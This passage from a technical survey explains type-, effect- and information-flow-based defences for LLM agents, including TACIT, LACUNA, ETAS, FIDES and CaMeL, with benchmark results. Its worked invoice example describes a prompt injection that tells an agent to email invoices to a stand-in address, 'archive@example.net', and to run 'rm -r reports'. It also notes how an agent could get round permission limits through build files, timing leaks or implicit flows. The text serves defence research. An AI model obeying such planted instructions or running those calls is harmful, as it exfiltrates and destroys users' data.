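Odersky and colleagues name several problems that TACIT doesn't address. One is external commands, which run outside Scala and are limited only by the list of permitted commands. They recommend allowing specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and the build tool `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. The sandbox matters even if only those two are allowed, because `sbt` runs code from the project's build files, and an agent that can edit those files and start `sbt` can run almost anything.

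Another gap is that timing can leak secrets. A pure function can take longer to run if a secret starts with A, so an agent that measures the delay learns something about the secret. One call might reveal a single bit, but the agent could repeat the process to learn more.

The type system also doesn't check whether a permitted action is correct. An agent with access to the reports folder can still overwrite the wrong report or save a wrong total. The type system doesn't control the order of permitted actions either, but Tan and colleagues' ETAS language can restrict that order.

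According to Glama, the wrapper protects the confidentiality of classified files but not their integrity. An agent can wrap any text and write it to a classified file, including the file that lists the SSH keys accepted for logging in to the machine. The operator can prevent this by making classified files read-only, which is not the default.

### LACUNA: typed gaps in a program

TACIT checks the programs that an agent sends to a tool server, while separate software runs the agent. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) puts the agent inside the program. A developer writes a gap, `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is a request in ordinary language and `T` is the type of the result. When the program reaches the gap, a language model writes code to fill it. The compiler checks that code as if the developer had written it, and returns any errors to the model for another attempt.

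In one example, a program has a variable `balance` with the value 100 and asks the agent to subtract 50 and return the new balance as a whole number. The model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces text instead of a number, so the compiler rejects both lines and the balance stays at 100. In a language that checks types only at run time, the subtraction would already have happened.

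The position of the gap also sets the agent's permissions, because with capture checking on, the generated code can use only the capabilities available at that point in the program. A developer can give one step a read-only file handle and no network access. Safe mode must also be on, because otherwise the code could use reflection or start an outside program without holding any capability.

LACUNA also makes classified data easier to work with. In TACIT, the outside model has to write the function for `map` before anyone knows what the text contains. In LACUNA, that function can contain a gap that a trusted local model fills with code after reading the text. The compiler checks the new code under the same rule, so it can't use any capability either.

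All of the roughly 400 test cases, some valid and some with typical mistakes, gave the expected result. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the programs DeepSeek V4 Flash wrote, and the agent answered 27.1% of the questions correctly.

LACUNA's results on τ²-bench were worse than TACIT's. DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calling. That is a loss of about 55 tasks, though Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calling. The compiler rejected 3.2% of Gemini's programs in the shop setting and 89% in the telecom setting, where most turns made no progress. Rejecting bad code keeps the agent within its permissions, but the agent can complete tasks only if it writes code the compiler accepts.

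In AgentDojo, attackers succeeded in seven of 949 trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and one of 949 with o4-mini-high. Zhao and colleagues point out that LACUNA doesn't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability that the task requires. For example, an agent that has to send email can send the wrong email. The limit on the agent's permissions is the same whichever model it uses, but the model still affects whether it makes that mistake.

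*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) also places agents inside a type-safe language, so that developers can reuse policy checks designed for ordinary programs. They wouldn't have to build a new checker for each agent, but they would need a suitable host language. Most agent frameworks use Python. Zhao and colleagues note that it can run generated code in place but can't provide the same guarantees.

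## Checking what a whole workflow may do, and in what order

TACIT's compiler checks which capabilities a program uses, but not the order in which it uses them. Some rules depend on order. For example, a company may require approval before any write to its code. A plain set of effects can't express this rule, because {approval, write} is the same set whichever comes first.

*Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (2026) gives more rules of this kind: a policy check must come before a refund, a file must not change after its anti-money-laundering check, and an agent may make at most two transfers. An agent can break any of these rules with calls that are individually legitimate, so a gate that checks one call at a time misses the violation.

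Most effect systems track only sets of effects and ignore program order, according to *Effect Systems as Abstract Interpretations* (2026), although some researchers added order fairly early. *Polymorphic Iterable Sequential Effect Systems* (2018) describes one such design, history effects, which summarise the sequences of events that code can produce. A separate program then compares the summary with a security policy. ETAS, the agent language by Tan and colleagues, builds a similar comparison into its compiler and combines it with run-time checks.

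### A repository review

An ETAS program consists mainly of tools, agents and flows (workflows). Each has an effect row, which lists the effects it may have on the outside world. An agent also has a list of the tools its model may request. In this simplified example, a model reads a code repository and proposes a patch, and the program asks a person before applying it:

```
tool read_repo(path: string) -> string  ![Repo.read]
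tool apply_patch(p: Patch)   -> unit    ![Repo.write]

@tools([read_repo])
agent Review(task: Task)     -> Patch   ![Repo.read]

flow review(task: Task) -> unit
  ![Repo.read, Approval.request, Repo.write] ~ ReviewPolicy
{
  let patch = Review.run(task);
  if approve("Apply this patch?", patch) {
    apply_patch(patch);
  }
}
```

The rows come after `!`, and `~ ReviewPolicy` attaches a rule about order. The agent can't apply a patch itself, because `apply_patch` isn't on its list. A row can also specify scope. For example, one of Tan and colleagues' tools has the effect `ProjectWorkspace.write<"reports/**">`, which covers any path under `reports/`.

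### Checking the order

The compiler derives two things about the effects of each expression:

```
Γ ⊢ e : T ! ε ▷ A
```

As in ordinary effect typing, e has type T and ε is its effect row. The new part, A, is an ordered summary of the requests that e may make. For the review it is:

```
Repo.read* ; Approval.request ; (nothing | Repo.write)
```

The star means "any number of times", and is used here because the number of files read depends on the model's output. The semicolon means "then", and the bar separates alternatives. ETAS also records the requests to the model, which this example leaves out.

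The rule could be:

```
spec ReviewPolicy = +Repo.read & +Approval.request & +Repo.write
                  & (Approval.request >> Repo.write)
```

A plus sign permits a request, and the rule forbids anything it doesn't permit. The last line requires an approval request before any write.

The compiler turns the rule into a monitor, a machine with a fixed number of states that changes state as requests arrive. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies*, introduced automata of this kind for specifying security policies. Here the monitor needs two ordinary states and one for violations:

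| Current state | After a read | After an approval request | After a write |
|---|---|---|---|
| No approval requested | no change | approval requested | **violation** |
| Approval requested | no change | no change | no change |

The compiler then runs the monitor over every sequence in the summary. The reads leave the monitor in its first state, and the approval request moves it to the second, which allows the write. No sequence reaches a violation, so the compiler has proved that the flow obeys the rule.

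Now suppose a developer moves the approval to the end:

```
let patch = Review.run(task);
apply_patch(patch);
approve("Keep this patch?", patch);
```

The effect row is still `[Repo.read, Approval.request, Repo.write]`, so an ordinary effect checker would accept the change. But the summary is now `Repo.read* ; Repo.write ; Approval.request`. The write occurs while the monitor is in its first state, so the compiler rejects the program.

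### Effects that a handler intercepts

A developer may want to test the flow without changing the repository. In ETAS, a handler can intercept an effect and supply a local result instead. A dry-run handler for `Repo.write`, for example, could report success without writing anything.

Earlier effect languages also have handlers, but they remove an effect from a function's type once a handler intercepts it. In Microsoft's research language Koka, a function that divides two numbers and may raise an exception has the type `(int,int) → exc int`. *Type Directed Compilation of Row-typed Algebraic Effects* (Leijen, 2016) wraps this function in a handler that returns 0 when the divisor is 0. The wrapped function has the type `(int,int) → ⟨⟩ int`, where `⟨⟩` is an empty effect row. This suits exceptions, because the row lists the effects the caller still has to handle. *Koka* (Leijen, 2014) proves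 that an expression without the exception effect in its type never throws an unhandled exception.

For an agent, it matters that it tried to write to the repository, even if a handler stopped the write. ETAS therefore removes the intercepted effect from the row but keeps the request in the summary. If the code inside the handler has row ε, the handler intercepts the effects in H, and the handler's own code has row εh, the new row is:

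```
(ε \ H) ∪ εh  =  ({Repo.write} \ {Repo.write}) ∪ ∅  =  ∅
```

This makes a second kind of edit detectable. Take a flow that is only supposed to read code, with the row `[Repo.read]` and the rule `+Repo.read`. A developer adds one line:

```
handle apply_patch(patch) with dry_run;
```

The handler removes the write, so the row is still `[Repo.read]`, but the summary becomes `Repo.read* ; Repo.write`. The rule doesn't permit a write, so the compiler rejects the program. The added line is harmless only because the handler stops it from changing the repository.

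Keeping handled requests also means a dry run has to follow the same rule as the real job, which can cause false alarms. If the repository review used a dry run to show the person a preview before asking for approval, the previewed write would break the rule. To avoid this, the developer would have to give previews their own effect.

### When the compiler cannot decide

Suppose the flow asks for approval only if the patch is longer than 20 lines, but applies the patch either way. The summary becomes:

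```
Repo.read* ; (nothing | Approval.request) ; Repo.write
```

Only one of the two alternatives breaks the rule. Under ETAS's formal rules, the compiler accepts such a program but keeps the monitor running with it. A long patch goes through after the approval request, but the monitor refuses a short one because it arrives without a request. Facts that exist only at run time, such as an exact file path or the age of an approval, must also be checked then.

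Residual, or leftover, monitors are older than AI agents. *Towards Runtime Adaptation of Actor Systems* (2017) describes Clara, a framework for the Java extension AspectJ. Clara's monitors watch only the events from program locations that static analysis failed to prove safe.

When an ETAS program makes a request, any active monitor checks it first. A matching handler can then intercept it. If none does, the host checks that the effect is within the declared row and that the host has granted permission for this particular action, then commits the effect (carries it out). The host still makes both checks when the compiler has proved the rule and removed the monitor. The log records requests, handled requests, commits and denials separately.

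As Basin (2012) summarises Schneider's result, monitoring can enforce only safety properties, which are rules whose violations show up at a definite point in a run. "Approval before any write" is a safety property, but "every incident ticket must eventually be closed" is not, because an open ticket might still be closed later.

One way around this is to set a deadline. *Agentproof* (2026), which checks agent workflow graphs, supports rules that require one event to follow another within k steps. The monitor for such a rule needs k + 2 states. Another way is to check the whole plan in advance. *CaMeLoT* (2026) does this with a temporal logic that can express "eventually", and rejects a plan that creates an incident ticket but never takes the required next step.

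### What Tan and colleagues prove

For a small core version of the language, Tan and colleagues prove two limits on every run:

```
requests so far  ∈  Pref(L(A))
committed effects  ⊆  ε
```

L(A) is the set of sequences the summary describes, and Pref adds the beginnings of those sequences, since a run may be incomplete. So the program never makes a request outside its summary, and the host never commits an effect outside the row. Requests that pass the checks also obey the rule, whether the compiler proved this in advance or left a monitor running during execution. These results hold for any reply from the model.

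These guarantees depend on every effect passing through the host. TACIT has the same requirement, so its users have to switch off the agent's other tools. The `write_file` tool that secretly reports to a metrics service would break the guarantee if it opened the network connection itself, because ETAS would record only the file write. For a third-party tool, the effect row is therefore only a declaration that someone has to verify by other means, such as source analysis.

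The approval rule is also weaker than it sounds, because it requires the program to request approval but not to receive it. If a developer deleted the `if`, so that the program applied the patch whatever the person answered, the program would still satisfy the rule by requesting approval before writing. A single request also satisfies the rule for every later write, even if it applies a different patch. To prevent both problems, the host has to grant permission only after the person agrees, and only for the patch they saw.

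### The safety tests

Tan and colleagues tested the safety checks on Nomo, a coding agent that they wrote in ETAS. The part they tested chooses whether to read a file or search the source code, and has 1,417 lines in 24 files. Local handlers supplied scripted model replies and tool results in ten scenarios. As expected, four scenarios finished normally and six stopped at the intended limit. The handlers intercepted all 19 requests (12 to the model, five file reads and two searches). Under these handlers, the program needed only one outside service, the console, but its summary still listed the model, read and search requests.

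They also gave the compiler six small programs, four of them deliberately broken:

| Program | Result |
|---|---|
| Approval before applying a change | accepted |
| The same flow with a dry-run handler | accepted |
| Approval left out | rejected, no guaranteed approval before the write |
| Approval moved after the change | rejected, for the same reason |
| Handled write under a read-only rule | rejected, the rule doesn't permit a write |
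| Unhandled write with an empty row | rejected, the effect is outside the row |

An ordinary effect checker would catch only the last of the four errors. The results show that the compiler can catch the other three, but six programs are too few to estimate reliably how often it would miss an error or reject valid code in a large project.

Tan and colleagues tested residual monitors in a separate Python model of the formal rules, not in the six programs. They compared the model's monitors for 384 rules with a direct check of every sequence of up to six requests, and all 419,712 comparisons agreed. But the compiler doesn't follow the formal rules exactly. Its analysis of the handled write is more precise, and it rejects that write outright, while the formal rules could leave a monitor running. The Python tests are therefore only indirect evidence about the compiler.

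Every model reply in the tests was scripted, so the tests include no adversarial model. They also include no third-party tools with hidden effects. The Nomo scenarios involve only reading and searching, so they don't test approvals or writes.

### Agents without a fixed workflow

ETAS can check the order of calls in advance because a developer has written the workflow as a program. A general-purpose agent chooses its next call as it goes. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system from Google for such agents, which enforces rules about the order of ordinary tool calls without requiring a new programming language. Before the agent starts, a separate language model writes a policy for the task. That model receives only the user's request and the tools' documentation, so text in an invoice can't influence the policy.

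For the invoice agent, the policy might be:

```
read_inbox . write_file(path="reports/march.txt")
           . send_email(to=FINANCE_MANAGER)
```

The dots mean "then". The fixed path and address matter more here than the order, because a data thief would also need the agent to read the inbox and then send an email. The policy doesn't restrict the body of the email, so the agent could still send the finance manager a false total. A policy can also refer to earlier results, for example by allowing a refund only to a sender and for an amount that the agent found in the transaction history.

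Tiffany and colleagues examined whether an attacker who fully controlled the agent could succeed without breaking the policy. The policies ruled out 93–95% of the attacks in AgentDojo. On Toolathlon, which has longer tasks, they ruled out 62–85%, about twice as many as simple lists of permitted tools did. The agents' success rate stayed within a few percent of its level without Sapien. But Sapien works only at run time, so it can stop a job halfway.

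Rules about order also depend on a reliable record of what happened before. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) checked recorded agent runs against five rules of the form "approval before a risky action". On AgentDojo runs with GPT-4o, the rules flagged 70.1% of the successful attacks, but also 36 of 123 harmless runs (29.3%). The logs contained no approvals, so the rules flagged every action of a risky type. In the banking tasks, where ordinary requests often involve payments, they flagged 79.2% of the harmless runs.

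Kekatos and colleagues got better results from rules that used data in the log, such as where a payee's details came from. But some of the text in the log comes from outsiders, so an attacker can exploit these rules too. One planted line defeated a simple check of this kind in 94–99% of the runs the check would otherwise have flagged. Accepting a value only from the lookup that was supposed to produce it stopped this attack without causing more false alarms.

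## Labelling data and checking it at each call

An agent can make the right calls in the right order and still put the wrong data in them. The gate can't detect this from the calls' effects, so it also has to check the data's labels, which record where the data came from and who may read it.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes the method in three steps. Developers label each source of data. Software joins the labels as data combine. Before each call, a policy engine compares the labels with the tool's policy, then allows the call, blocks it or refers it to a person for approval. The engine doesn't use the language model to decide, so an instruction planted in an email can't make it allow an exception.

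Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, define two basic policies, which Kolluri and colleagues later named:

```
trusted action:   the call's integrity is trusted
permitted flow:   every recipient is among the data's readers
```

The first policy is for tools with serious consequences, and the second is for tools that send data out. A designer can also allow a call to a tool that sends data out if the call meets either policy. The agent may then send data to someone who isn't on the reader list, but only if no untrusted text influenced the decision, in which case the user is assumed to have wanted it.

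### The invoice job, call by call

Suppose the inbox holds two invoices, from the suppliers Arden and Birch. The clerk who runs the agent and the finance manager can both read the inbox, and each supplier can read its own invoice.

| Data | Integrity | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| The clerk's request | trusted | anyone |
| Arden's invoice | untrusted | clerk, manager, Arden |
| Birch's invoice | untrusted | clerk, manager, Birch |
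| A summary of both invoices | untrusted | clerk, manager |

The last label is the join of the two above it. Arden may not read the summary, because it includes Birch's prices.

An attacker posing as Arden has added an instruction to the first invoice, telling the agent to send both invoices to `archive@example.net` and then delete the reports folder. In the simplest kind of agent, the model reads the invoices directly. Every later call then has the label "untrusted; clerk, manager", because anything the model has read may have influenced that call.

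| Call | Policy | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `read_inbox("invoices")` | none | allowed |
| `write_file("reports/march.txt", summary)` | trusted action | **blocked**, the call is untrusted |
| `lookup_vat(number)` | either | **blocked**, the call is untrusted and the operator is not a reader |
| `send_email(FINANCE_MANAGER, summary)` | either | allowed, the manager is a reader |
| `send_email("archive@example.net", invoices)` | either | blocked, the call is untrusted and the attacker is not a reader |
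| `run_shell("rm -r reports")` | trusted action | blocked, the call is untrusted |

The last two calls come from the planted instruction, and the gate stops both. The results in bold are false alarms. The gate can't distinguish the clerk's file from one the attacker asked for, because both requests come from a model that has read the invoice.

The email to the manager goes through, possibly with a false total, because permitted flow limits only where data can go.

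The same policy can catch honest mistakes. In one of Microsoft's examples, an agent answering a user's email has read a preview of the quarterly sales from one colleague and is about to include the figures in a reply to another, who isn't allowed to see them yet. Only the user is allowed to read both emails, so the gate doesn't let the agent send the reply on its own.

### Explicit and implicit flows

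Copying an invoice total into an email is an explicit flow, because the data themselves move. An implicit flow reveals data through what the program does:

```
if overdue:
    send_email(OUTSIDER, "hello")
```

The message contains nothing private, but anyone who knows the program can conclude from its arrival that the company is behind on its payments.

Type systems for information flow handle this with a program-counter label, written pc. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, trace the idea to work by Dorothy and Peter Denning in the 1970s. The pc is the join of the labels of all the conditions that led the program to its current line. With ⊑ for "may flow to", the main rules are:

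```
x = e         allowed if  label(e) ⊔ pc ⊑ label(x)
send(r, e)    allowed if  label(e) ⊔ pc ⊑ label(r)
if e: body    check the body with  pc ⊔ label(e)
```

In the example, the pc is public before the `if` but private inside it because `overdue` is private. An outsider may receive only public data, so the type checker rejects the email even though "hello" itself is public.

These rules are meant to ensure noninterference, which means that changing a program's private inputs can't change its public outputs. The matching property for integrity is that changing the untrusted inputs can't change the trusted outputs. If the invoice agent had this second property, no text in an invoice could affect which files it deleted.

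Language models complicate the definition because they choose their replies partly at random, so two runs can differ even when the inputs are identical. Garby and colleagues compare the probabilities of the visible results instead. As is usual in this field, they allow a secret to affect whether a program finishes, and they prove a limit on how much else it can affect:

```
difference between the two distributions  ≤  (d1 + d2) / 2
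```

Here d1 and d2 are the probabilities that the program fails to finish when run with the first secret and the second secret, respectively. If it always finishes, the visible results have exactly the same probabilities whatever the secret is.

### What one run cannot show

Noninterference is a statement about pairs of runs, but a run-time monitor sees only one. A classic example, which Garby and colleagues credit to J. S. Fenton, shows why this matters. Here it is with the overdue payments:

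```
1  a = True
2  b = True
3  if overdue: a = False
4  if a: b = False
5  if b: send_email(OUTSIDER, "hello")
```

Suppose the monitor tracks the pc and marks a variable private when the program changes it under a private condition:

| After line | If payments are overdue | If they are not |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | `a` is False and private | `a` is True and public |
| 4 | `b` is True and public | `b` is False and public |
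| 5 | the email goes out | no email |

The email goes out exactly when payments are overdue, but in both runs the monitor finds only a public condition on line 5. In the first run, the leak depends on an assignment on line 4 that the program skips. A type checker reads the skipped code too, so it would require `a` and then `b` to be private, and would reject the email.

A stricter monitor can still prevent the leak, for example by stopping any program that is about to change a public variable under a private condition. It would stop this program on line 3 if payments were overdue. But it would also stop harmless programs, such as one that never uses `a` again. Anyone who notices that this program stopped also learns that payments were overdue. The definition that Garby and colleagues use permits this second leak.

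### Declassification and endorsement

Full noninterference would rule out much of an accounts department's ordinary work, even looking up a VAT number from a private invoice. Practical systems therefore allow two controlled exceptions: declassification, which lets more people read a piece of data, and endorsement, which marks untrusted data as trusted.

The department would be safer declassifying only VAT numbers that already appear in its list of suppliers. If it declassified anything in the format of a VAT number, an attacker might get part of a bank account number declassified by fitting it into that format.

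Endorsement is safest when there are few possible values. Garby and colleagues give the example of an agent that sorts an email into one of a fixed set of categories and uses the category as the subject of its reply. With n categories, an attacker controls at most log₂ n bits. If the invoice agent chose from "routine", "disputed" and "overdue", the attacker would control at most about 1.6 bits. They could get an invoice into the wrong category but couldn't write the subject line.

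In their language, endorsing a value changes its integrity label but not its confidentiality label. They prove that no use of endorsement can therefore leak secrets. The proof assistant Lean has checked both this theorem and the noninterference theorem, and the interpreter that runs the agents is part of the same Lean code.

### How FIDES hides untrusted data

FIDES, the planner that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, avoids many of the false alarms in the invoice table by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the calls. Its state consists of the conversation so far, a label for that conversation, and a memory of named variables with their own labels. Each round works as follows:

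1. The model's reply gets the join of the labels of everything the model received, since nobody can say exactly which parts influenced it.
2. If the reply requests a tool call, FIDES fills in any variables among the arguments and checks the tool's policy.
3. The tool's result gets the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and the data the tool read.
4. If that label is more restrictive than the conversation's, FIDES stores the result in a new variable and shows the model only the variable's name.

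FIDES can apply the last step to each field separately, so the model might see the date of an email while the body stays hidden.

For the invoice job, the calls would be:

```
read_inbox("invoices")                  → #inbox
query_llm("Summarise these", #inbox)    → #summary
write_file("reports/march.txt", #summary)
send_email(FINANCE_MANAGER, #summary)
```

Both variables have the label "untrusted; clerk, manager", but the conversation remains trusted. The decision to write the file is therefore trusted, so the agent can make the call that the simpler agent couldn't. `query_llm` passes the invoices to a second model that has no tools. The planted instruction reaches only that model, which may write a bad summary but can't send or delete anything. Simon Willison proposed this division of work in 2023 as the dual-LLM pattern.

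The call's arguments also need checking. Suppose the planner asks the second model for Arden's VAT number and passes the answer to `lookup_vat`. The decision to make the call is trusted, so a policy that checks only the decision would allow it, even if the planted text had made the second model return Birch's bank details. Costa and colleagues' basic definition of trusted action also covers the arguments, but the version they tested ignores them. A department that used the tested version would need a separate check on the number.

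### Constrained inspection

Some tasks depend on what the hidden data contain. If the clerk wants a calendar entry only when an email contains a meeting request, the planner has to find out whether the email contains one. It can open the variable with a tool called `inspect`, but this adds the whole email to the conversation, which makes the conversation untrusted.

A narrower way is to ask the second model a yes-or-no question and open only the answer. FIDES can restrict the form of the answer while the model is producing it, and it adds the answer's type to the label. It orders these types by how much information they can carry, from true-or-false values through fixed lists to free text. A policy can then let a consequential action depend on an untrusted yes or no, because an attacker controls only one bit, although that bit can still matter a lot if the question is whether to pay an invoice.

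For secrets, FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. It covers data that move directly but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of calls. An agent that wrote "hello" only when payments were overdue would therefore satisfy it. Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference would forbid almost any publicly visible action once the agent had read a secret. Garby and colleagues reply that a reviewer can't tell from a given run whether a value that FIDES let through was an intended exception or a leak.

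### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks and on the same tasks with prompt injections. With GPT-4o, an unprotected agent carried out 152 injected tasks. FIDES with its policy checks off carried out 21, and with the checks on it carried out none. (AgentDojo's own scoring gives FIDES three failures in the last case, which the researchers rejected after looking at each one.)

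This table shows the percentage of ordinary tasks that each agent completed when nobody attacked it:

| Model | Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | unprotected | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o | labels and policies only | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o | FIDES | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1 | unprotected | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1 | labels and policies only | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
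| o1 | FIDES | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

Averaged over the four groups, hiding data in variables gains 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1. Protection still reduces task completion considerably. With o1, FIDES completes about 61% of tasks on average, compared with 84% for the unprotected agent. Costa and colleagues also report a gap of only 6.3 points, but they measured it with the policy checks off.

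Some of the loss is intentional, because several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, which the policies are meant to prevent. Other failures came from model errors, such as mixing up variable names. Kolluri and colleagues later improved the results by telling the planner which policies applied.

No attack succeeded, which shows that the enforcement worked but provides little evidence about the labelling. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so the labels were certain to cover every attack. A real department doesn't have a list of the attacks it will face. The tested version also left out the restriction on the form of answers, so the results don't show how well that restriction works.

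### What developers must label

Microsoft released FIDES in May 2026 as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its library for building agents. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), developers have to label the data that their tools return, mark the tools that must refuse to run after the agent has read untrusted content, and set the highest confidentiality level that each outgoing tool accepts. The framework carries the labels from call to call and checks these policies.

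If a developer forgets to label a tool, the framework treats its results as trusted and public. The Model Context Protocol's hints, by contrast, default to the most cautious values. If nobody labelled `read_inbox`, both invoices would count as trusted and public, and every call in the invoice table would pass, including the two from the attacker. Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead.

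The framework hides untrusted results in variables by default. A developer can turn this off, which makes an agent easier to debug, but a single untrusted result then makes the rest of the run untrusted.

Programs can also pass labels to each other in an existing metadata field of the Model Context Protocol. GitHub's tool server, for example, labels content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private repositories as private and trusted. Labelling private content as trusted can be wrong, since an employee can paste a customer's email into a private repository. Microsoft has a gateway that adds labels and policies for servers without them, but someone has to write a labelling function and choose a policy for every tool.

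### CaMeL writes the plan first

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues took a stricter approach in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In their system, CaMeL, one model reads only the user's request and writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. For the invoice job, the plan might be:

```
invoices = read_inbox("invoices")
summary = query_ai_assistant(f"Summarise: {invoices}", str)
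write_file("reports/march.txt", summary)
send_email(FINANCE_MANAGER, summary)
```

The plan is complete before the agent opens an invoice, so an instruction planted in one can't add a step. An interpreter then runs the program and records each value's sources and who may read it. Here `summary` inherits the sources and readers of `invoices`. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks these records and allows or refuses the call. As in FIDES, a second model without tools processes the untrusted text.

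A FIDES planner can look at a result and change course, but looking at it makes the planner's conversation untrusted. CaMeL's planner has to write any alternatives into the program beforehand. In an extreme case from tests by Garby and colleagues, a planner asked to follow the instructions in a file wrote a loop with a branch for each available tool, so the file's text could determine the calls. With the policy checks off, an attack through that file succeeded without changing the plan.

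### CaMeL's results and later changes

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) reports a 67% completion rate for CaMeL on AgentDojo and attributes many of the failures to policies that treat all untrusted data as equally risky. In a later rerun for *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks (29.9%). The rerun used an adapted version of the software, which may explain part of the difference in completion rates.

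Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, and compared it with Randori, an agent written in their own language:

| Model | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on | Randori |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 18 of 48 | 36 of 48 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 18 of 48 | 31 of 48 |

In these tests, most of the difference between CaMeL's two columns comes from the policies, since the plan-first design is the same in both. Randori's advantage is harder to interpret because it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and its plans may endorse untrusted data. Without endorsement, its score with MiMo-v2.5 fell to 26.

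Attackers succeeded in two of Randori's 1,296 attacked runs across three models. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to a file that the attacker had replaced. The low success rate overstates how much the labels contributed. In about two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, an ordinary plan would never contain the calls the attacker needed, so the attack would fail without any labels. The other 423 runs tested the label checks.

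Garby and colleagues also found leaks in CaMeL. Its interpreter tracks the pc but has the weakness shown by the five-line program above, because it raises a variable's label only on the branch that runs. A second leak is in an ordinary Python loop, outside the interpreter, that asks for a new plan when one fails. Whether a policy blocks a plan can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit, and a program that keeps trying can recover the whole secret. Randori avoids this by testing its plan in an artificial environment with no untrusted data and using the real inbox only after the plan works.

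*CaMeLoT* does some of the label checks before any tool runs. It labels each variable in the plan with its origin and can reject a plan that would send a message to an address the second model extracted from untrusted text. The planner then gets a description of the failing path and can try again.

Agents that operate a computer through its screen are a harder case because the planner can't know what will appear. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner prepare for many possibilities. The average plan contained 39.7 branches, compared with 3.7 on AgentDojo. The agent kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models. But an attacker can influence which branch runs. If the plan includes closing cookie notices, an attacker can get the agent to click on an advertisement that looks like one.

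This is an implicit flow from untrusted data to an action. A pc label would reveal it, but almost every click depends on what is on the screen, so a policy of trusted action would block nearly all clicks. Foerster and colleagues left out tool policies because a click has no fixed meaning that a policy could refer to.

Labels can also get lost when one agent hands work to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends CaMeL's interpreter so that a value keeps its recorded origin across agents, and the receiving agent's planner can't read untrusted content as an instruction.

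### Correct labels and correct policies

The guarantees of FIDES and CaMeL hold only if the labels and tool policies are correct. Both systems also trust the user, the planning model and the tools' code.

Labels can be wrong even when every source has one. Costa and colleagues treated an email's sender and recipients as its only readers, although someone may have shared it more widely. Tallam and Miller question the assumption that a user's request is safe. If the clerk pasted text from Arden's invoice into the request, and that text included the planted instruction, the instruction would be labelled as trusted and the planner would read it.

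Policies go wrong when they don't match what a tool does. Suppose the `write_file` tool with the hidden metrics has only the trusted-action policy. The clerk's request is trusted, so the call passes, and information about a private file leaves the company without any check on who may read it. The `net.write` in the tool's effect set shows that it also needs the permitted-flow policy.

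## Following influence through the language model

Even with correct labels and sensible policies, a gate can flag almost every call because labels spread through the language model. In ordinary code, each line shows which variables it reads, so labels can follow the data. A model's reply may depend on anything in its context, so it gets the join of all the labels there. Costa and colleagues call this rule sound but possibly too conservative. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), finding a more precise rule is still an open problem.

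### One invoice in ten messages

Suppose the clerk gives the agent three small jobs in one conversation, and the model reads Arden's invoice directly. `write_file` requires a trusted action. `send_email` requires either a trusted action or a recipient who is allowed to read everything in the conversation.

| | Message | Conversation's label | Gate |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Clerk: "Summarise Arden's invoice" | trusted | |
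| 2 | Model calls `read_inbox` | trusted | allows |
| 3 | The invoice arrives | untrusted | |
| 4 | Model writes the summary | untrusted | |
| 5 | Clerk: "Save a note that we close on Friday" | untrusted | |
| 6 | Model calls `write_file` | untrusted | asks the clerk |
| 7 | Tool confirms that it saved the file | untrusted | |
| 8 | Clerk: "Email that note to Birch" | untrusted | |
| 9 | Model calls `send_email` | untrusted | asks the clerk |
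| 10 | Tool confirms that it sent the email | untrusted | |

A join never moves back towards "trusted", so one invoice marks every later call as untrusted. Both questions to the clerk are false alarms, since the note has nothing to do with the invoice. But the gate can't rule out that the invoice contained an instruction such as "add our new bank details to every note you save". The email also fails the reader test, because Birch isn't allowed to read Arden's invoice.

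Researchers call this label creep. If the gate blocks such calls, the agent is nearly useless after the first email it reads. If it asks the user to approve each one, *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) warns that tired users start approving requests without thinking. A new conversation would clear the label, but the agent would no longer know which note "that note" was. FIDES hides the invoice in a variable, which postpones the problem until the planner has to read it.

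### Answering again from fewer messages

A model often needs only part of its context. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, use this to give some replies a less restrictive label:

1. Run the model on the full context and keep its answer, y.
2. Choose a less restrictive label L, remove every message above it, and measure how likely the model still finds y.
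3. Accept L if the loss is at most a chosen tolerance λ.
4. Run the model again on the remaining messages alone, and return only the new answer.

The test in step 3 is:

```
U(y | all messages) − U(y | messages at or below L)  ≤  λ
```

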